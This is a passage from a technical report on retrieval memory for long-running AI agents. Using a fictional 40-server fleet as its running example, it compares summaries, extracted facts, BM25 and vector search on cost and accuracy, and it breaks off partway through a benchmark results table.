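# Retrieval memory for long-running AI agents, and why command logs and host records are harder to retrieve than prose

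## How an agent uses a database as its memory

An AI agent is a language model that works towards a goal by repeatedly calling tools. It runs a command or a search, reads the output and chooses its next step. Retrieval memory is a database that the agent writes to and searches, so that information outlasts a single run. Engineers add it when the work goes on for weeks, because the model retains nothing from earlier runs and can read only a limited amount of text at once. Each entry, called an item, may be a note that the agent wrote, a line from a log or a structured record that a machine produced. The search has to return the few items relevant to the agent's next decision.

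### Why nothing carries over between sessions

Training sets a language model's parameters, the numbers that determine how it turns input text into output text, and answering a request doesn't change them. OpenAI tells developers that each text generation request is "independent and stateless", and according to Anthropic's *Using the Messages API*, a program must by default resend the whole conversation with every request. Both companies also offer to store the transcript on their own servers, but the model still has to process it again each time. Anthropic's stored transcript expires five minutes after the last request, and the feature is still in beta. OpenAI's can last longer than the 30 days that the company keeps ordinary responses, but when a developer chains responses together, OpenAI bills all the earlier input again.

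The amount of text an agent can read at once is limited by its context window, the largest number of tokens (words or fragments of words) that one request can hold. By OpenAI's definition, this includes the answer and any reasoning the model writes before it. When a session, or one run of an agent, ends, its working text is lost unless it has been stored. Du (2026), in *Memory for Autonomous LLM Agents*, imagines a debugging assistant that has to relearn the layout of the same codebase every Monday and retries the fix that crashed the build on Friday.

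A simpler remedy than a database is to have the model summarise its history and carry the summary forward. Du objects that every round of summarising drops rare details. For example, an instruction never to call the production database directly may survive the first round and be gone by the third. Du's example is hypothetical, but Packer, Wooders and colleagues (2023) measured something close to it in *MemGPT*. They took chats that ran over five sessions and had a model write questions that only someone who knew those sessions could answer. GPT-4 Turbo got 35.3 per cent right with a summary of the sessions and 93.4 per cent with a search over the full transcript, as judged by another model. Five sessions come to about sixty messages, or some 3,000 tokens at the message length the paper assumes elsewhere, so the whole transcript would have fitted into GPT-4 Turbo's context window. The gap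 therefore measures what a summary loses. It doesn't show how search compares with reading the whole transcript. Reading everything is easy for sixty messages but impractical for months of work on many machines.

### Forty web servers

The running example in this report is a fictional fleet of 40 web servers, web-01 to web-40, which an agent looks after for three months. The agent installs upgrades, answers alerts and investigates incidents, so it must be able to recall what anyone did to which machine, when, and with what result. If each server logs 500 commands a day and each line takes 50 tokens, 90 days produce 1.8 million lines and 90 million tokens. A context window of a million tokens would hold just over one per cent of that.

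Three items from the night of 14 September show what the memory contains. The agent wrote this note at the end of the incident:

> 14 September, web-17. Site returned 502 errors from 02:10. After the upgrade to version 3.8 the shop application kept hitting its 512 MB memory limit and crashing. Raised the limit to 768 MB and restarted the service. Errors stopped at 02:31.

A 502 error is what a web server returns when the program behind it gives no valid answer. The restart also left a line in the command log, the record of the commands that people and programs run on a machine:

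```
2026-09-14T02:29:47Z web-17 user=deploy pid=48213 cmd="sudo systemctl restart shop-app" exit=0
```

A second later the machine produced a host record, a structured entry about something that happened on it, in this case the start of a process:

```
{"time": "2026-09-14T02:29:48Z", "host": "web-17", "event": "process_start",
 "pid": 48219, "parent_pid": 1, "user": "shop", "exe": "/usr/bin/python3"}
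```

The note, the log line and the host record all belong to the same repair. The note gives the reason and the outcome. The log line gives the exact command and the account that ran it, and its "exit=0" means only that the restart command succeeded. The host record doesn't include the shop application's service name or mention the restart, but it has the same hostname as the log line and a time within a second of it. The hostname and the process numbers (pid) are identifiers, strings that name one particular thing.

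### Writing, maintaining and reading

Du reduces an agent with memory to two formulas:

```
aₜ   = π(xₜ, R(Mₜ, xₜ), gₜ)
Mₜ₊₁ = U(Mₜ, xₜ, aₜ, oₜ, rₜ)
```

At step t the agent receives an input x, such as an alert. The function R reads the memory M and returns the items relevant to the alert. The model π produces an action a from the alert, those items and the agent's current goals g. The function U then updates the memory using the input, the action, the feedback o from the environment and any reward signal r. *Memory in the Age of AI Agents* (Hu, Liu and colleagues, 2025) divides this update into formation, which turns raw material into candidate items, and evolution, which fits the candidates into the existing store.

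On web-17 the loop starts when the agent calls a tool with the text of its note. Ordinary code then saves the text with the time, the hostname and the source. Docker provides a memory tool like this that keeps its items in SQLite, a small database stored in one file. Because the model decides when to write, it has to be prompted to do so before the session ends. Anthropic's *Memory tool* gives Claude models a directory of notes that a developer can back with a database. It comes with a standing instruction to look in the directory first, record progress along the way and expect the context window to be reset at any moment. MemGPT warns the model when the prompt fills, say, 70 per cent of the window. When the window is full, MemGPT removes messages that take up about half of it, replaces them with a summary and keeps the originals in a searchable database.

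Next the database indexes the note so that a search can find it without reading every item. A word index lists which items contain which words. A vector index holds an embedding for each item, which is a list of numbers that a separate model computes from the text. The model is meant to give texts with similar meanings lists that are close together. By default, the list has 1,536 numbers for the smaller of the two models in OpenAI's *Vector embeddings* and 3,072 for the larger. The current model in Google's *Embeddings* also produces 3,072 numbers and accepts at most 8,192 tokens of text, so an incident report longer than that has to be split first.

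The agent also maintains its memory between writes. Du insists that U does more than append items. It should also merge duplicates, settle contradictions, rank items by priority and sometimes delete them, including stale items, which were true when written but no longer are. If web-18 and web-20 crash in the same way after their upgrades, the agent can combine three notes into one item stating that version 3.8 needs 768 MB.

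*Generative Agents* (Park, O'Brien and colleagues, 2023) automated this kind of generalising for the inhabitants of a simulated village. A language model rated the importance of every new record from 1 (brushing teeth) to 10 (a break-up). Once the ratings of recent events added up to more than 150, the program showed the model the latest 100 records and asked for three questions it could answer from them. The program then searched the memory for each question and had the model write down conclusions. It saved each conclusion to the memory with pointers to the supporting records. This happened two or three times per simulated day.

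On 5 October an alert reports that web-19 is returning 502 errors. The agent has to write a search query, and the alert's own text may be a poor one. Du gives the example of a user who asks "Why did that crash?" The log that answers the question may be from two sessions earlier and share almost no wording with it. The model can rewrite its input before searching, or send several differently worded queries and combine the results. For this alert, it might search for earlier 502 errors on any web server, with their causes and fixes. Some embedding models also require each text to be marked as a query or a document to search, and Google recommends a different fixed format for each.

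The search itself comes in two main forms. Word matching ranks items by the words they share with the query, usually with the BM25 formula. Vector search computes an embedding of the query and returns the items whose embeddings lie closest to it, and the usual measure of closeness is cosine similarity:

```
cos(q, d) = (q · d) / (|q| × |d|)
```

The numerator multiplies the two vectors number by number and adds up the products. The denominator multiplies the lengths of the two vectors, where a vector's length is the square root of the sum of its squared numbers. The result ranges from −1 for vectors that point in opposite directions to 1 for vectors that point in the same direction.

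Suppose embeddings had three numbers instead of 3,072. The agent's query becomes q = (2, 1, 2), the note on web-17 becomes a = (1, 2, 2), and a note about renewing a security certificate becomes b = (2, 2, −1). Each vector has length 3, because the squares of its numbers add up to 9.

```
cos(q, a) = (2×1 + 1×2 + 2×2)    / (3×3) = 8/9 ≈ 0.89
cos(q, b) = (2×2 + 1×2 + 2×(−1)) / (3×3) = 4/9 ≈ 0.44
```

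The note on web-17 ranks first. Doubling every number in a would give (2, 4, 4) and the same score, 16/18, because cosine similarity depends only on direction. OpenAI scales its embeddings to length 1, so the division is unnecessary. A hostname, date or outcome affects the score only as far as the embedding model has encoded it in the numbers.

A memory can add such considerations outside the embedding. Park and colleagues scored each record by adding its cosine similarity, its importance rating and a recency value, each rescaled to lie between 0 and 1. The recency value is multiplied by 0.995 for every hour since a search last returned the record. *Beyond Memory Leaderboards* (2026) reports that most retrieval-based memories still use this scheme, but its settings were chosen for characters in a simulated village. By 5 October, three weeks have passed since the repair on web-17. If no search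 has returned the note since then, its recency value is 0.995⁵⁰⁴, or about 0.08 before rescaling. That decay is sensible for a character planning a party, but for an engineer the last comparable crash may be the most useful record in the store, however long ago it happened.

A program then copies the best items into the prompt as plain text beside the alert. Space is limited here too, so MemGPT returns search results in pages to keep a broad query from filling the context window. With the September note in its prompt, the model raises the memory limit on web-19, restarts the service and watches the error rate. It then saves a new note, which records that the fault and the repair were the same as before and that the errors stopped after two minutes. The next search for 502 errors will return both notes.

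### A fixed library and a memory that the agent writes

The search step in this loop is older than the write step. Lewis, Perez and colleagues (2020), in *Retrieval-Augmented Generation for Knowledge-Intensive NLP Tasks*, joined a language model to a searchable index of Wikipedia. They called the method retrieval-augmented generation, or RAG, a name that now covers any system that searches a store and puts the results in the prompt before the model answers. In 2023, MemGPT gave a model functions for writing to and editing its own store, modeled on the way an operating system moves data between main memory and disk. *Generative Agents*, the same year, gave each simulated villager a time-stamped record of everything it perceived. Many designs followed, and a December 2025 survey by Hu and colleagues found that papers on "agent memory" differed drastically in implementation, objectives and assumptions.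 Du published another survey in March 2026. In May, Luo, Tian and colleagues (2026), in *From Storage to Experience*, sorted the designs into three stages: keeping a faithful record, correcting it, and drawing general rules from many episodes.

The original form of RAG retrieves from a fixed collection of text. Lewis and colleagues split a December 2018 copy of Wikipedia into 21 million 100-word passages, computed an embedding for each, and kept the index unchanged while they trained the rest of the system. They could update the system's knowledge by replacing the index. People had written and corrected the passages beforehand, and the model's answers could not change them.

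An agent's memory includes the agent's own output. Hu and colleagues use this to distinguish it historically from classical RAG, which reads static sources, while agent memory keeps adding what the agent does and how its environment responds. They also acknowledge that the distinction has blurred, since both kinds of system rely on the same vector indexes and some RAG systems now refine their stores as they run. For example, Anthropic uses RAG to search a user's past conversations with Claude, and Claude wrote half of each conversation. The search technique matters less than whether the model is reading text it wrote earlier, because it then receives its own past mistakes as evidence.

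Suppose the agent misread the incident on web-17. A web crawler had been overloading the application and happened to leave at 02:30, just after the restart, but the agent credited the higher memory limit in its note. In October the agent reads the note, applies the same change to web-19, sees the errors stop when the crawler leaves, and records a second success. Every later search returns two notes that credit the memory limit. Du warns that "one bad write can pollute the store" for many steps. Du also describes the opposite mistake, in which an agent wrongly concludes that some call always fails, avoids it, and so never collects the evidence that would correct it. Luo and colleagues cite two studies from 2025 in which a memory that grew without restriction made agents perform worse, because errors spread through it.

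RAG over an encyclopedia can also fall back on what the model learned in training. On one standard set of questions, Lewis and colleagues' model correctly answered 11.8 per cent of those for which no retrieved passage contained the correct answer. The server agent lacks this fallback because no training text describes what happened on web-17.

One safeguard is to make every general conclusion cite the episodes behind it, as Park and colleagues' program did. Du recommends this but acknowledges that the cited episodes may be unrepresentative, as both crawler nights would be. Du also advises keeping the full raw records alongside the agent's summaries. On servers, these records are especially useful because the machines produced them independently of the agent's interpretation. Host records from 14 September showing that the application exited for lack of memory would support the note, while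 complete records with no such exit would be strong evidence against it. To check, the agent has to find a few entries among 1.8 million log lines and any accompanying host records.

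## Deciding what to store and whether retrieval is needed

Search is only one way to give an agent access to its past. While the agent repairs web-17, its program can resend the entire session with every request. The program can also replace old messages with a running summary, let the agent keep notes in files, extract facts into database fields, or store items and retrieve a few at a time.

| Method | What it preserves | What it loses | What it costs |
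|---|---|---|---|
| Resend the whole history | Every word, in order | Nothing, until the history outgrows the context window | The model rereads everything on every turn |
| Running summary | The main events and the current state | Exact wording, and details that looked unimportant at the time | A model call for every compression |
| Notes in files | Whatever the agent wrote down | Whatever it didn't write down | Tokens for writing, then tool calls to find and read the right file |
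| Facts in fields | The values that the fields provide for | Everything that has no field | A model call or a parser for each new piece of history |
| Stored items with retrieval | The original text of every item | Nothing from the store, but the model sees only what the search returns | Indexing, a search per question and a few thousand tokens of results |

A cruder program drops the oldest messages. *BudgetBench* (2026) uses this truncation as a baseline because it needs no extra model call, embedding model or store.

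Summaries change the wording of what they keep. In *Fidelity Before Structure*, An (2026) gives the example of a programmer who says "Please use type hints everywhere" early in a long discussion. The summary keeps the preference for type hints but drops "everywhere". When An planted facts in artificial conversations and asked about them later, rolling summaries led to an exact answer 14.0 per cent of the time, against 91.0 per cent for retrieval of the original wording. Summaries also use more compute than they seem to, since long inputs in the pilot of *BudgetBench* set off one compression call after another.

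Extraction loses whatever the extracting model doesn't recognise as worth keeping. Pollertlam and Kornsuwannawit (2026), in *Beyond the Context Window*, tested extraction with Mem0, an open-source library in which a model extracts short facts from a conversation and stores them for vector search. Mem0 reduced conversations of about 101,600 tokens to an average of 2,909 tokens of facts. One question asked how many days had passed between a user's visits to two museums. Mem0 had stored an interest in art-themed day trips but no dates, so the model answered zero. The same model correctly answered seven when it read the full conversation. Log lines carry less of this risk because their time, host and user are in fixed places, so ordinary code can copy them into fields and keep the original line as well.

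Files can hold the agent's notes or the raw history. With notes, as with summaries, the agent has to guess what it will need. Raw files lose nothing, but the agent must search them with commands such as grep, which prints the lines that contain a given string.

### What it costs to reread everything

Suppose each turn of the agent's loop adds 2,000 tokens of commands, output and reasoning. If the program resends everything, the model reads 2,000 tokens on the first turn, 4,000 on the second and 200,000 on the hundredth. If the program instead sends a fixed 6,000 tokens of instructions, recent messages and search results, the model reads the same amount on the hundredth turn as on the first.

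```
resend everything:  2,000 × (1 + 2 + … + 100) = 2,000 × 5,050 = 10,100,000 tokens
retrieve:           6,000 × 100                               =    600,000 tokens
```

The resending total grows with the square of the number of turns. Doubling the session to 200 turns would raise it to 40.2 million tokens, but would only double the retrieval total. Anthropic's *Pricing* lists Claude Opus 5.5 at $4 per million input tokens, so 100 turns would cost $40.40 with resending and $2.40 with retrieval, excluding the model's output.

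Prompt caching removes most of that difference. The provider keeps its processed form of a prompt for a short time and charges less when the next request begins with the same text. On Opus 5.5, writing to a five-minute cache costs $5 per million tokens and reading from it costs $0.20. In the example, the program writes each of the 200,000 tokens once and rereads the earlier ones on every later turn:

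```
write:   0.2 million × $5.00 = $1.00
reread:  9.9 million × $0.20 = $1.98
total:                         $2.98   (retrieval without a cache: $2.40)
```

The order reverses on Anthropic's most expensive general model, Claude Fable 5.2. It costs $8 per million input tokens but only $0.20 per million for cache reads, according to Vonk (2026), in *Claude Fable 5.2 is out*. If cache writes cost Anthropic's usual 1.25 times the input price, resending comes to $3.98 and retrieval to $4.80, so adding retrieval may not save money in a session of this length.

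The discount applies only if the beginning of the prompt stays the same and the requests follow each other closely. A program that rewrites a summary at the top of the prompt pays the full price for everything after it. If every turn in the example came after the five-minute cache had expired, the program would write all 10.1 million tokens to the cache again and pay $50.50, more than without caching. A one-hour cache costs $8 per million tokens to write. During an incident, the server agent's turns are seconds apart, so resending the session is cheap. But the repair on web-17 and the alert on web-19 are three weeks apart, which is longer than any cache lasts.

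Longer context windows postpone the problem. At 2,000 tokens a turn, a million-token window fills after 500 turns. By then, on Opus 5.5, resending the cached history has cost $54.90, compared with $12 for retrieval. Anthropic charges the same rate per token for a request of 900,000 tokens as for one of 9,000, but resending still costs more because the total number of tokens reread grows with the square of the number of turns.

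Extraction adds an initial expense, which Pollertlam and Kornsuwannawit set against the cost of rereading over N questions:

```
whole history:    C(N) = C_first + (N − 1) × C_cached
extracted facts:  C(N) = C_write + N × C_read
```

For a history of about 100,000 tokens, the first question cost $0.0265 with the whole history and $0.0450 with Mem0, which had to build its store first. Mem0 became cheaper at about the tenth question and was 26 per cent cheaper by the twentieth. These figures assume that cached tokens cost a tenth of the normal price. At a twentieth, which Anthropic now charges on Opus 5.5, the same formulas put the break-even point at about the twentieth question. Mem0 also answered far fewer questions correctly, 49.0 per cent compared with 82.4 per cent for the whole history.

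### Seven strategies on the same conversations

*Retrieval Beats Cheap Structured Memory* (August 2026) compared seven strategies on two public sets of long conversations, with a language model judging the answers. The strategies were full context, truncation, a running summary, append-only notes, fields filled by a small language model, BM25 retrieval, and a combination of fields with retrieval. One set, LoCoMo, consists of chats between two speakers across many dated sessions. The other, LongMemEval, gives each question its own history of chats with an assistant.

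BM25 was the best of the cheap methods. On 160 LoCoMo questions about conversations of 369 to 680 messages, it used 98 per cent less input than full context and cost 95.2 per cent less. It answered 39.4 per cent of the questions correctly, compared with 30.6 per cent for full context. Chance could explain that difference (p = 0.09), and the paper estimates that it would take 360 to 430 questions to confirm it. The result therefore supports the claim that retrieval saved money without a detectable loss of accuracy, but it doesn't establish that retrieval was more accurate.

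The fields did worst, although they had been expected to do well on facts that change. A model with 8 billion parameters extracted the values, and each field held only the latest one. On 72 questions about updated facts, the fields produced 37.5 per cent correct answers and BM25 73.6 per cent. An extractor with 70 billion parameters raised the fields' score by 29.2 points, with 23 answers becoming right and 2 becoming wrong. That net gain of 21 matches a set of 72 questions, which would put the fields at about 67 per cent, still below BM25. The larger extractor also made the method cost 1.8 times as much as full context. The fields were workable, but a model cheap enough to fill them didn't extract values well enough.

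Retrieval did poorly on questions that combine several messages. Across all 281 such questions in LoCoMo, BM25 found only about 13 per cent of the messages that contained the evidence. It also trailed full context by 10.2 points on 254 LongMemEval questions about dates, several sessions at once, or things the history didn't contain. Only the combination of fields and retrieval matched full context on those questions. An agent's question such as "which servers did I change after the upgrade?" is of this kind, since the answer is spread across many records.

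### Scoring what the agent does

A server agent has to act on what it remembers, and a correct answer to a question doesn't guarantee a correct action. *When Does Memory Help?* (Mishra and Mishra, 2026) introduces MERIT, a benchmark that scores actions. In each session, an agent talks to a simulated user and calls tools that change a small database. The agent succeeds only if the database fails a set condition at the start of the session and meets it at the end. One of the three domains is IT operations, where the agent can search logs, read and change configurations, and deploy software versions.

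Four to six sessions form a group. In an early session the user establishes a fact, for example the configuration change that would fix an incident, and forbids the agent to act on it yet. In the hardest version, a later session revises the fact. A further session then sets a task that requires the latest value. Before the run, a program checks that the value appears neither in that session's input nor in the initial database. Agents without any memory consequently succeeded in at most 5 per cent of the hardest tasks. The results for IT operations were as follows, with the same model writing the memory in every case:

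| Memory | Claude Haiku 4.5 | GPT-4.1 | GPT-4.1 mini |
|---|---|---|---|
| All earlier sessions in full | 100% | 100% | 100% |
| Summary, rewritten after each session | 100% | 90% | 80% |
| Facts in fields, overwritten when revised | 100% | 100% | 90% |
| Vector search over earlier sessions | 95% | 45% | 38% |

Vector search returned old and revised values together, and the models differed in how well they chose between the two. Mishra and Mishra tested a newer model, Claude Sonnet 5, only on customer support. It still succeeded less often with vector search (75 per cent) than with a summary or fields (100 per cent).

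Summaries did well in MERIT, but An's rolling summaries answered only 5.7 per cent of 699 LoCoMo questions correctly. Much of the difference comes from the tasks. A group in MERIT has at most six sessions and a handful of facts that matter, so a summary can hold all of those facts. A LoCoMo conversation has about 300 messages, and the questions may concern any detail in them. For the server fleet, a summary could hold the shop application's current memory limit but not three months of commands.

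In 55 of the hardest tasks, vector search gave the agent the correct latest value, but in 25 of those the agent still didn't act on it, a failure that better search can't fix. In IT tasks that required several facts, success was 100 per cent when the program filled the fields using patterns written by hand for the domain, and 40 per cent when a general language model extracted the facts. Log lines have a regular format, so hand-written patterns are a realistic option for them.

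The methods differed less in price than in reliability. On the easiest customer-support tasks, a session cost $0.00046 without memory, $0.00066 with fields, $0.00073 with vector search and $0.00126 with full replay. Success in MERIT reflects caution as well as memory. When Claude Opus 4.8 had all earlier sessions in its prompt, it completed only 75 per cent of the revised refunds. Its transcripts showed that it recalled the amounts but sought confirmation from a supervisor.

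### Whether elaborate structures beat plain retrieval

Many memory systems extract facts from text, classify them and link them in a graph, on the assumption that the result is easier to search than the original. To test this, An changed only the stored items and kept the search, the answering model and the judge the same. One store held the conversation in pieces of 512 characters, and the other held facts that GPT-4o mini had extracted and sorted into eight types, each with a short quotation from the source. The plain pieces scored 43.9 per cent on LoCoMo and 67.4 per cent on LongMemEval, compared with 28.0 and 45.4 per cent for the extracted facts. Linking the facts in a graph didn't close the gap. Storing both kinds of item together scored 42.5 per cent on LoCoMo, too close to the score for plain pieces to count as a loss.

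*MemoryTax* (Peng, 2026) repeated the comparison with current models on one LoCoMo conversation of 419 messages and 152 questions. Zep, one of the systems compared, builds a graph of facts and records when each was true. Pi, a coding agent, received the raw conversation as a file and searched it with its own tools.

| Method | Correct with GPT-4o mini | Correct with Claude Opus 5.5 | Total cost with Opus 5.5 |
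|---|---|---|---|
| Full context | 74% | 95% | $17.84 |
| BM25 over raw messages | 74% | 90% | about $2 |
| Mem0 | 78% | 95% | about $37 |
| Zep | 43% | 87% | about $7.40 |
| Pi with a raw file | 63% | 99% | $6.95 |

Mem0 helped the weak model and added nothing for the strong one. Searching a file worked far better with the strong model. Two other coding agents, Codex and Claude Code, scored below 30 per cent with GPT-4o mini, which often answered without opening the file, and at least 97 per cent with Opus 5.5. The file included photo captions that the other methods didn't receive, which inflated Pi's lead over full context. On the 88 questions that didn't depend on photos, Pi scored 100 per cent and full context 99. Peng ran each combination only once.

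Building the Mem0 store with Opus 5.5 cost $25.88 for a conversation of under 29,000 tokens. At that rate, extracting facts from the fleet's 90 million tokens of command log would cost about $80,000. Even GPT-6 Luna, a much cheaper model in the same study, would cost about $1,400. Paying these rates makes sense for a few thousand incident notes but hardly for 1.8 million log lines, most of which nobody will ever ask about.

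The evidence for structured memory comes from better designs than the ones that lost in comparisons. *LYCHEEMEMORY V2* (Li, Liu and colleagues, 2026) groups related messages before a model extracts anything from them. The model then writes self-contained records, replacing pronouns with names and "last Tuesday" with a date. Each record lists the people and things it concerns, the time, and a link to the original messages. With GPT-4.1 mini, the system correctly answered 89.2 per cent of LoCoMo questions and 92.2 per cent of LongMemEval questions. It scored over 20 points more than A-Mem, an earlier system of linked notes, and used 86 per cent fewer tokens to build its LoCoMo store.

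Those percentages can't be compared with An's because the studies used different models, questions and judges. With the entire LoCoMo conversation in the prompt, models scored 30.6 per cent in *Retrieval Beats Cheap Structured Memory*, 59.9 per cent in An's study, 92.9 per cent in Pollertlam and Kornsuwannawit's and 95 per cent in Peng's, so only comparisons within a study mean much. Li and colleagues' system searches the raw messages as well as its records, so its success is compatible with An's result, which concerns systems that discard the original wording.

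The amount of text the model may read also affects the outcome. *FlexA-Mem* (2026) reports that with a budget of 4,000 tokens, a method that recovers the original text answered 78.0 per cent of LongMemEval questions, 25.9 points more than A-Mem. Plain keyword retrieval came within 0.7 points of that method. At 32,000 tokens A-Mem was ahead, by 88.6 to 85.7 per cent. How the program searches may matter as much as what it stores. In *Diagnosing Retrieval vs. Utilization Bottlenecks in LLM Agent Memory*, Yuan, Su and Yao (2026) combined three ways of writing memories with three ways of searching them. Average accuracy on LoCoMo ranged from 57.1 to 77.2 per cent depending on the search method.

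Most of this evidence comes from chats, which differ from an agent's own work. *Exploring Cross-Scenario Generality of Agentic Memory Systems* (2026) tested eight memory systems on five families of tasks. On records of agents at work, structures fixed in advance lost individual steps and actions, which are what a command log is meant to preserve. An agent that searched the material when a question arrived did best across the tasks.

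The case for storing structure is stronger when the answer doesn't resemble the question. *depth not length*, a paper on a software vendor's website, considers decisions that are several causal steps away from the current task. For example, the memory limit on web-19 matters because of version 3.8, which the agent may have installed because of a security flaw. A note about that flaw has little in common with an alert about 502 errors. The paper argues that the chance of finding such a note by similarity falls steeply with every step, while following a stored link takes about the same amount of work each time. In a related case from An's experiments, where each planted fact fitted the extraction format exactly and questions combined two or three facts, the extracted facts passed 81.0 per cent of the tests and the plain pieces about 25 per cent.

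Engineers should generally keep the raw text and add structure only where they know in advance what the agent will ask. For servers, that means leaving the command log as it is and recording the agent's decisions in a fixed format. The two stores can then remain separate. *Did You Check the Right Pocket?* found that going directly to the right store gave more accurate answers with fewer tokens than searching every store. But its selector was given the right store in advance, so one that has to choose would gain less.

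### What to record about a decision

A decision record needs to state what the agent did, to what, why, with what result and when, and to point to the raw evidence. For the repair on web-17 it could look like this:

```
action:   raised memory limit from 512 MB to 768 MB, restarted shop-app
target:   web-17, shop-app 3.8
reason:   502 errors since 02:10; application kept hitting its limit and crashing
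outcome:  no 502 errors after 02:31
time:     2026-09-14T02:29:47Z (restart)
source:   command log, web-17, 2026-09-14T02:29:47Z, pid 48213
```

The agent has to record the reason at the time, because the command log doesn't contain it. The outcome should be an observation, such as "no 502 errors after 02:31", rather than an explanation such as "the higher limit fixed the errors", which would be wrong if the errors stopped because a web crawler left. The agent should add the outcome only after checking it.

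The target is the easiest part to lose in a summary. Suppose a summary reduces the record of a repair on web-17 to "14 September: after the upgrade a web server ran out of memory. Raised the limit to 768 MB, errors stopped." In November an engineer wants to undo the change and asks which server it was. A repair on web-23 would have produced the same summary, so a model that sees only this text cannot tell which server was changed. If all 40 servers are equally likely, its best guess is right one time in 40. A better model or embedding would not help, because both would start from the same words. A search for "web-17" also no longer finds the item.

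Peng's study shows the same limit in practice. When GPT-4o mini wrote Zep's graph, GPT-4o mini answered 43 per cent of the questions from it, and the far stronger Claude Opus 5.5 answered only 45 per cent. Opus 5.5 answered 87 per cent when it had also written the graph. Engineers who save money by using a weaker model to write the memory can't make up for it later by using a stronger model to read it.

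If a summary is poor, the agent may still find the missing detail in the raw log, but the date alone may not be enough to locate it. If the agent restarted the shop application on twelve servers that night, twelve log entries will match. The pointer in the decision record identifies a single line, but it works only while that line exists. The program must therefore keep the log for as long as any decision cites it, or copy the cited lines into the record. Keeping everything takes little storage, since the fleet's 90 million tokens come to about 360 MB by Anthropic's rule of thumb of four characters per token.

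At 20 decisions a day, three months produce 1,800 decision records. At 150 tokens each, they total 270,000 tokens and fit in a million-token context window. Opus 5.5 could read all of them for $1.08 without a cache, so the agent could review every decision before a major change and use retrieval for routine alerts. The command log is more than 300 times larger, and the agent can use it only through search.

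## Choosing between word matching and vector search

An agent can search the fleet's 1.8 million log lines by their words or by their embeddings. Word matching finds the line that contains web-17 or a particular process number, but it misses a note that describes the same event in other words. Vector search can find that note, but it may rank a line about web-18 as high as one about web-17. Because the two methods fail in different cases, combining their results usually works better than using either alone. A slower model can then reorder the best candidates.

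### How BM25 weighs words

BM25 scores an item by adding up a contribution from every query word that the item contains. *Learning What to Fail On* (2026) gives the formula with these settings:

```
score(q, d) = sum over the words t in q of

      IDF(t) × tf × (k₁ + 1)
  ─────────────────────────────────────      k₁ = 1.5,  b = 0.75
  tf + k₁ × (1 − b + b × |d| / avgdl)
```

Here tf is the number of times the word occurs in item d, |d| is the item's length in words, and avgdl is the average length of all items. IDF stands for inverse document frequency, a weight that is larger for rarer words. In a common version, N is the number of items in the store and n is the number that contain the word:

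```
IDF(t) = ln(1 + (N − n + 0.5) / (n + 0.5))
```

In an index of 100,000 log lines, the hostname of a database server, db-03, might occur in 50 lines, while "nginx", the name of a common web server program, might occur in 20,000.

```
IDF("db-03") = ln(1 + 99,950.5 / 50.5)      ≈ 7.6
IDF("nginx") = ln(1 + 80,000.5 / 20,000.5)  ≈ 1.6
```

A match on the hostname therefore counts almost five times as much as a match on "nginx". A word that occurs in every line has a weight close to zero.

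The rest of the formula adjusts for repetition and length. In a line of average length, one occurrence multiplies the weight by 1, two by 1.43 and ten by 2.17. The multiplier never reaches 2.5, so repeating "nginx" adds at most 4.0 to a line's score, less than the 7.6 from a single "db-03". In an item twice the average length, one occurrence multiplies the weight by 0.69, because a long text is more likely to contain any word by chance.

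In the fleet's log, web-17 occurs in about one line in 40, which gives it a weight of 3.7. A process number that occurs in only one of the 1.8 million lines has a weight of 14. BM25 therefore gives the most weight to the strings that narrow a search most, provided the index keeps them whole. If the indexing program splits "web-17" at the hyphen, the "17" also matches dates and port numbers.

BM25 matches words without regard to meaning. If an engineer searches for "checkout page down, ran out of RAM", the agent's note about web-17 scores zero because it shares no words with the query, even though it mentions 502 errors, a memory limit and crashing.

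### How many result sets one vector can produce

Vector search can match "RAM" to "memory", but each item has to fit into one embedding. *On the Theoretical Limitations of Embedding-Based Retrieval* (Weller, Boratko and colleagues, 2025) proves that an embedding's dimension (how many numbers it contains) limits which sets of items a search can return together.

Suppose a store holds n items, and for every possible set of k items there must be a query that returns exactly that set. All vectors have length 1. The items in the set must also beat all other items by a clear gap, so that small errors don't change the result. If each of them scores at least 2γ higher than any item outside the set, then γ is the margin, and the number of dimensions d must satisfy:

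```
d ≥ log C(n, k) / log(1 + 1/γ)
```

C(n, k) is the number of ways to choose k items out of n. The proof compares two different sets, A and B, whose queries have the vectors u_A and u_B. Since the sets differ, some item i is only in A and some item j is only in B. Item i must score higher for u_A, and item j must score higher for u_B:

```
u_A · (vᵢ − vⱼ) ≥ 2γ
u_B · (vⱼ − vᵢ) ≥ 2γ
(u_A − u_B) · (vᵢ − vⱼ) ≥ 4γ      (the sum of the two lines above)
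```

Since vᵢ and vⱼ have length 1, vᵢ − vⱼ has length at most 2. The sum can then reach 4γ only if u_A and u_B are at least 2γ apart. This holds for every pair of sets, so balls of radius γ around the query vectors do not overlap. All of them lie inside a ball of radius 1 + γ. In d dimensions, volume grows with the radius to the power d, so the small balls fit only if C(n, k) × γᵈ ≤ (1 + γ)ᵈ. Taking logarithms gives the bound.

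For a million items, sets of ten and a margin of 0.1, the calculation is:

```
C(1,000,000, 10) ≈ 2.8 × 10⁵³
d ≥ ln(2.8 × 10⁵³) / ln(11) ≈ 123 / 2.4 ≈ 51.3, so at least 52
```

Current embeddings with 3,072 numbers far exceed that bound. The bound rises to 425 for sets of 100 and to 3,296 for sets of 1,000, which is more numbers than those embeddings have.

The bound assumes that users want every combination of notes, but nobody will ask for most of the 2.8 × 10⁵³ possible sets of ten. Weller and colleagues reply that queries with several conditions make more combinations plausible, and that search agents increasingly write such queries. For example, "Restarts after the 3.8 upgrade that didn't stop the errors" could match almost any group of notes. Still, the theorem doesn't identify which realistic queries will fail.

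The bound is also only a minimum. Bangachev, Bresler and colleagues (2026), in *Is Dimensionality a Barrier for Retrieval Models?*, worked out how many dimensions are enough. The largest margin that any embedding can achieve for all sets of k items in a store of n is about 1/(2√k), and reaching it takes a number of dimensions proportional to k × log(n/k). A margin of 0.1 is therefore achievable for sets of ten, where the maximum is about 0.16, but not for sets of 100, where the maximum is 0.05 however many dimensions are used. The number of dimensions needed grows slowly with the size of the store. Going from a million items to a billion raises it by about 60 per cent for sets of ten, so a growing memory is unlikely to fail simply because its embeddings have too few dimensions.

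### The LIMIT test and its reversal

To test real models, Weller and colleagues built a dataset called LIMIT. It has 50,000 short documents, each listing fewer than 50 things that an invented person likes. Each of the 1,000 queries asks who likes one particular thing, and exactly two documents are correct. All the correct documents come from a pool of 46, the smallest pool with enough pairs (1,035) to give each query a different one.

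The measure is recall@k, the share of relevant items that appear among the first k results. The embedding models in this table used their full number of dimensions:

| Method | Recall@2 | Recall@10 | Recall@100 |
|---|---|---|---|
| BM25 | 85.7% | 90.4% | 93.6% |
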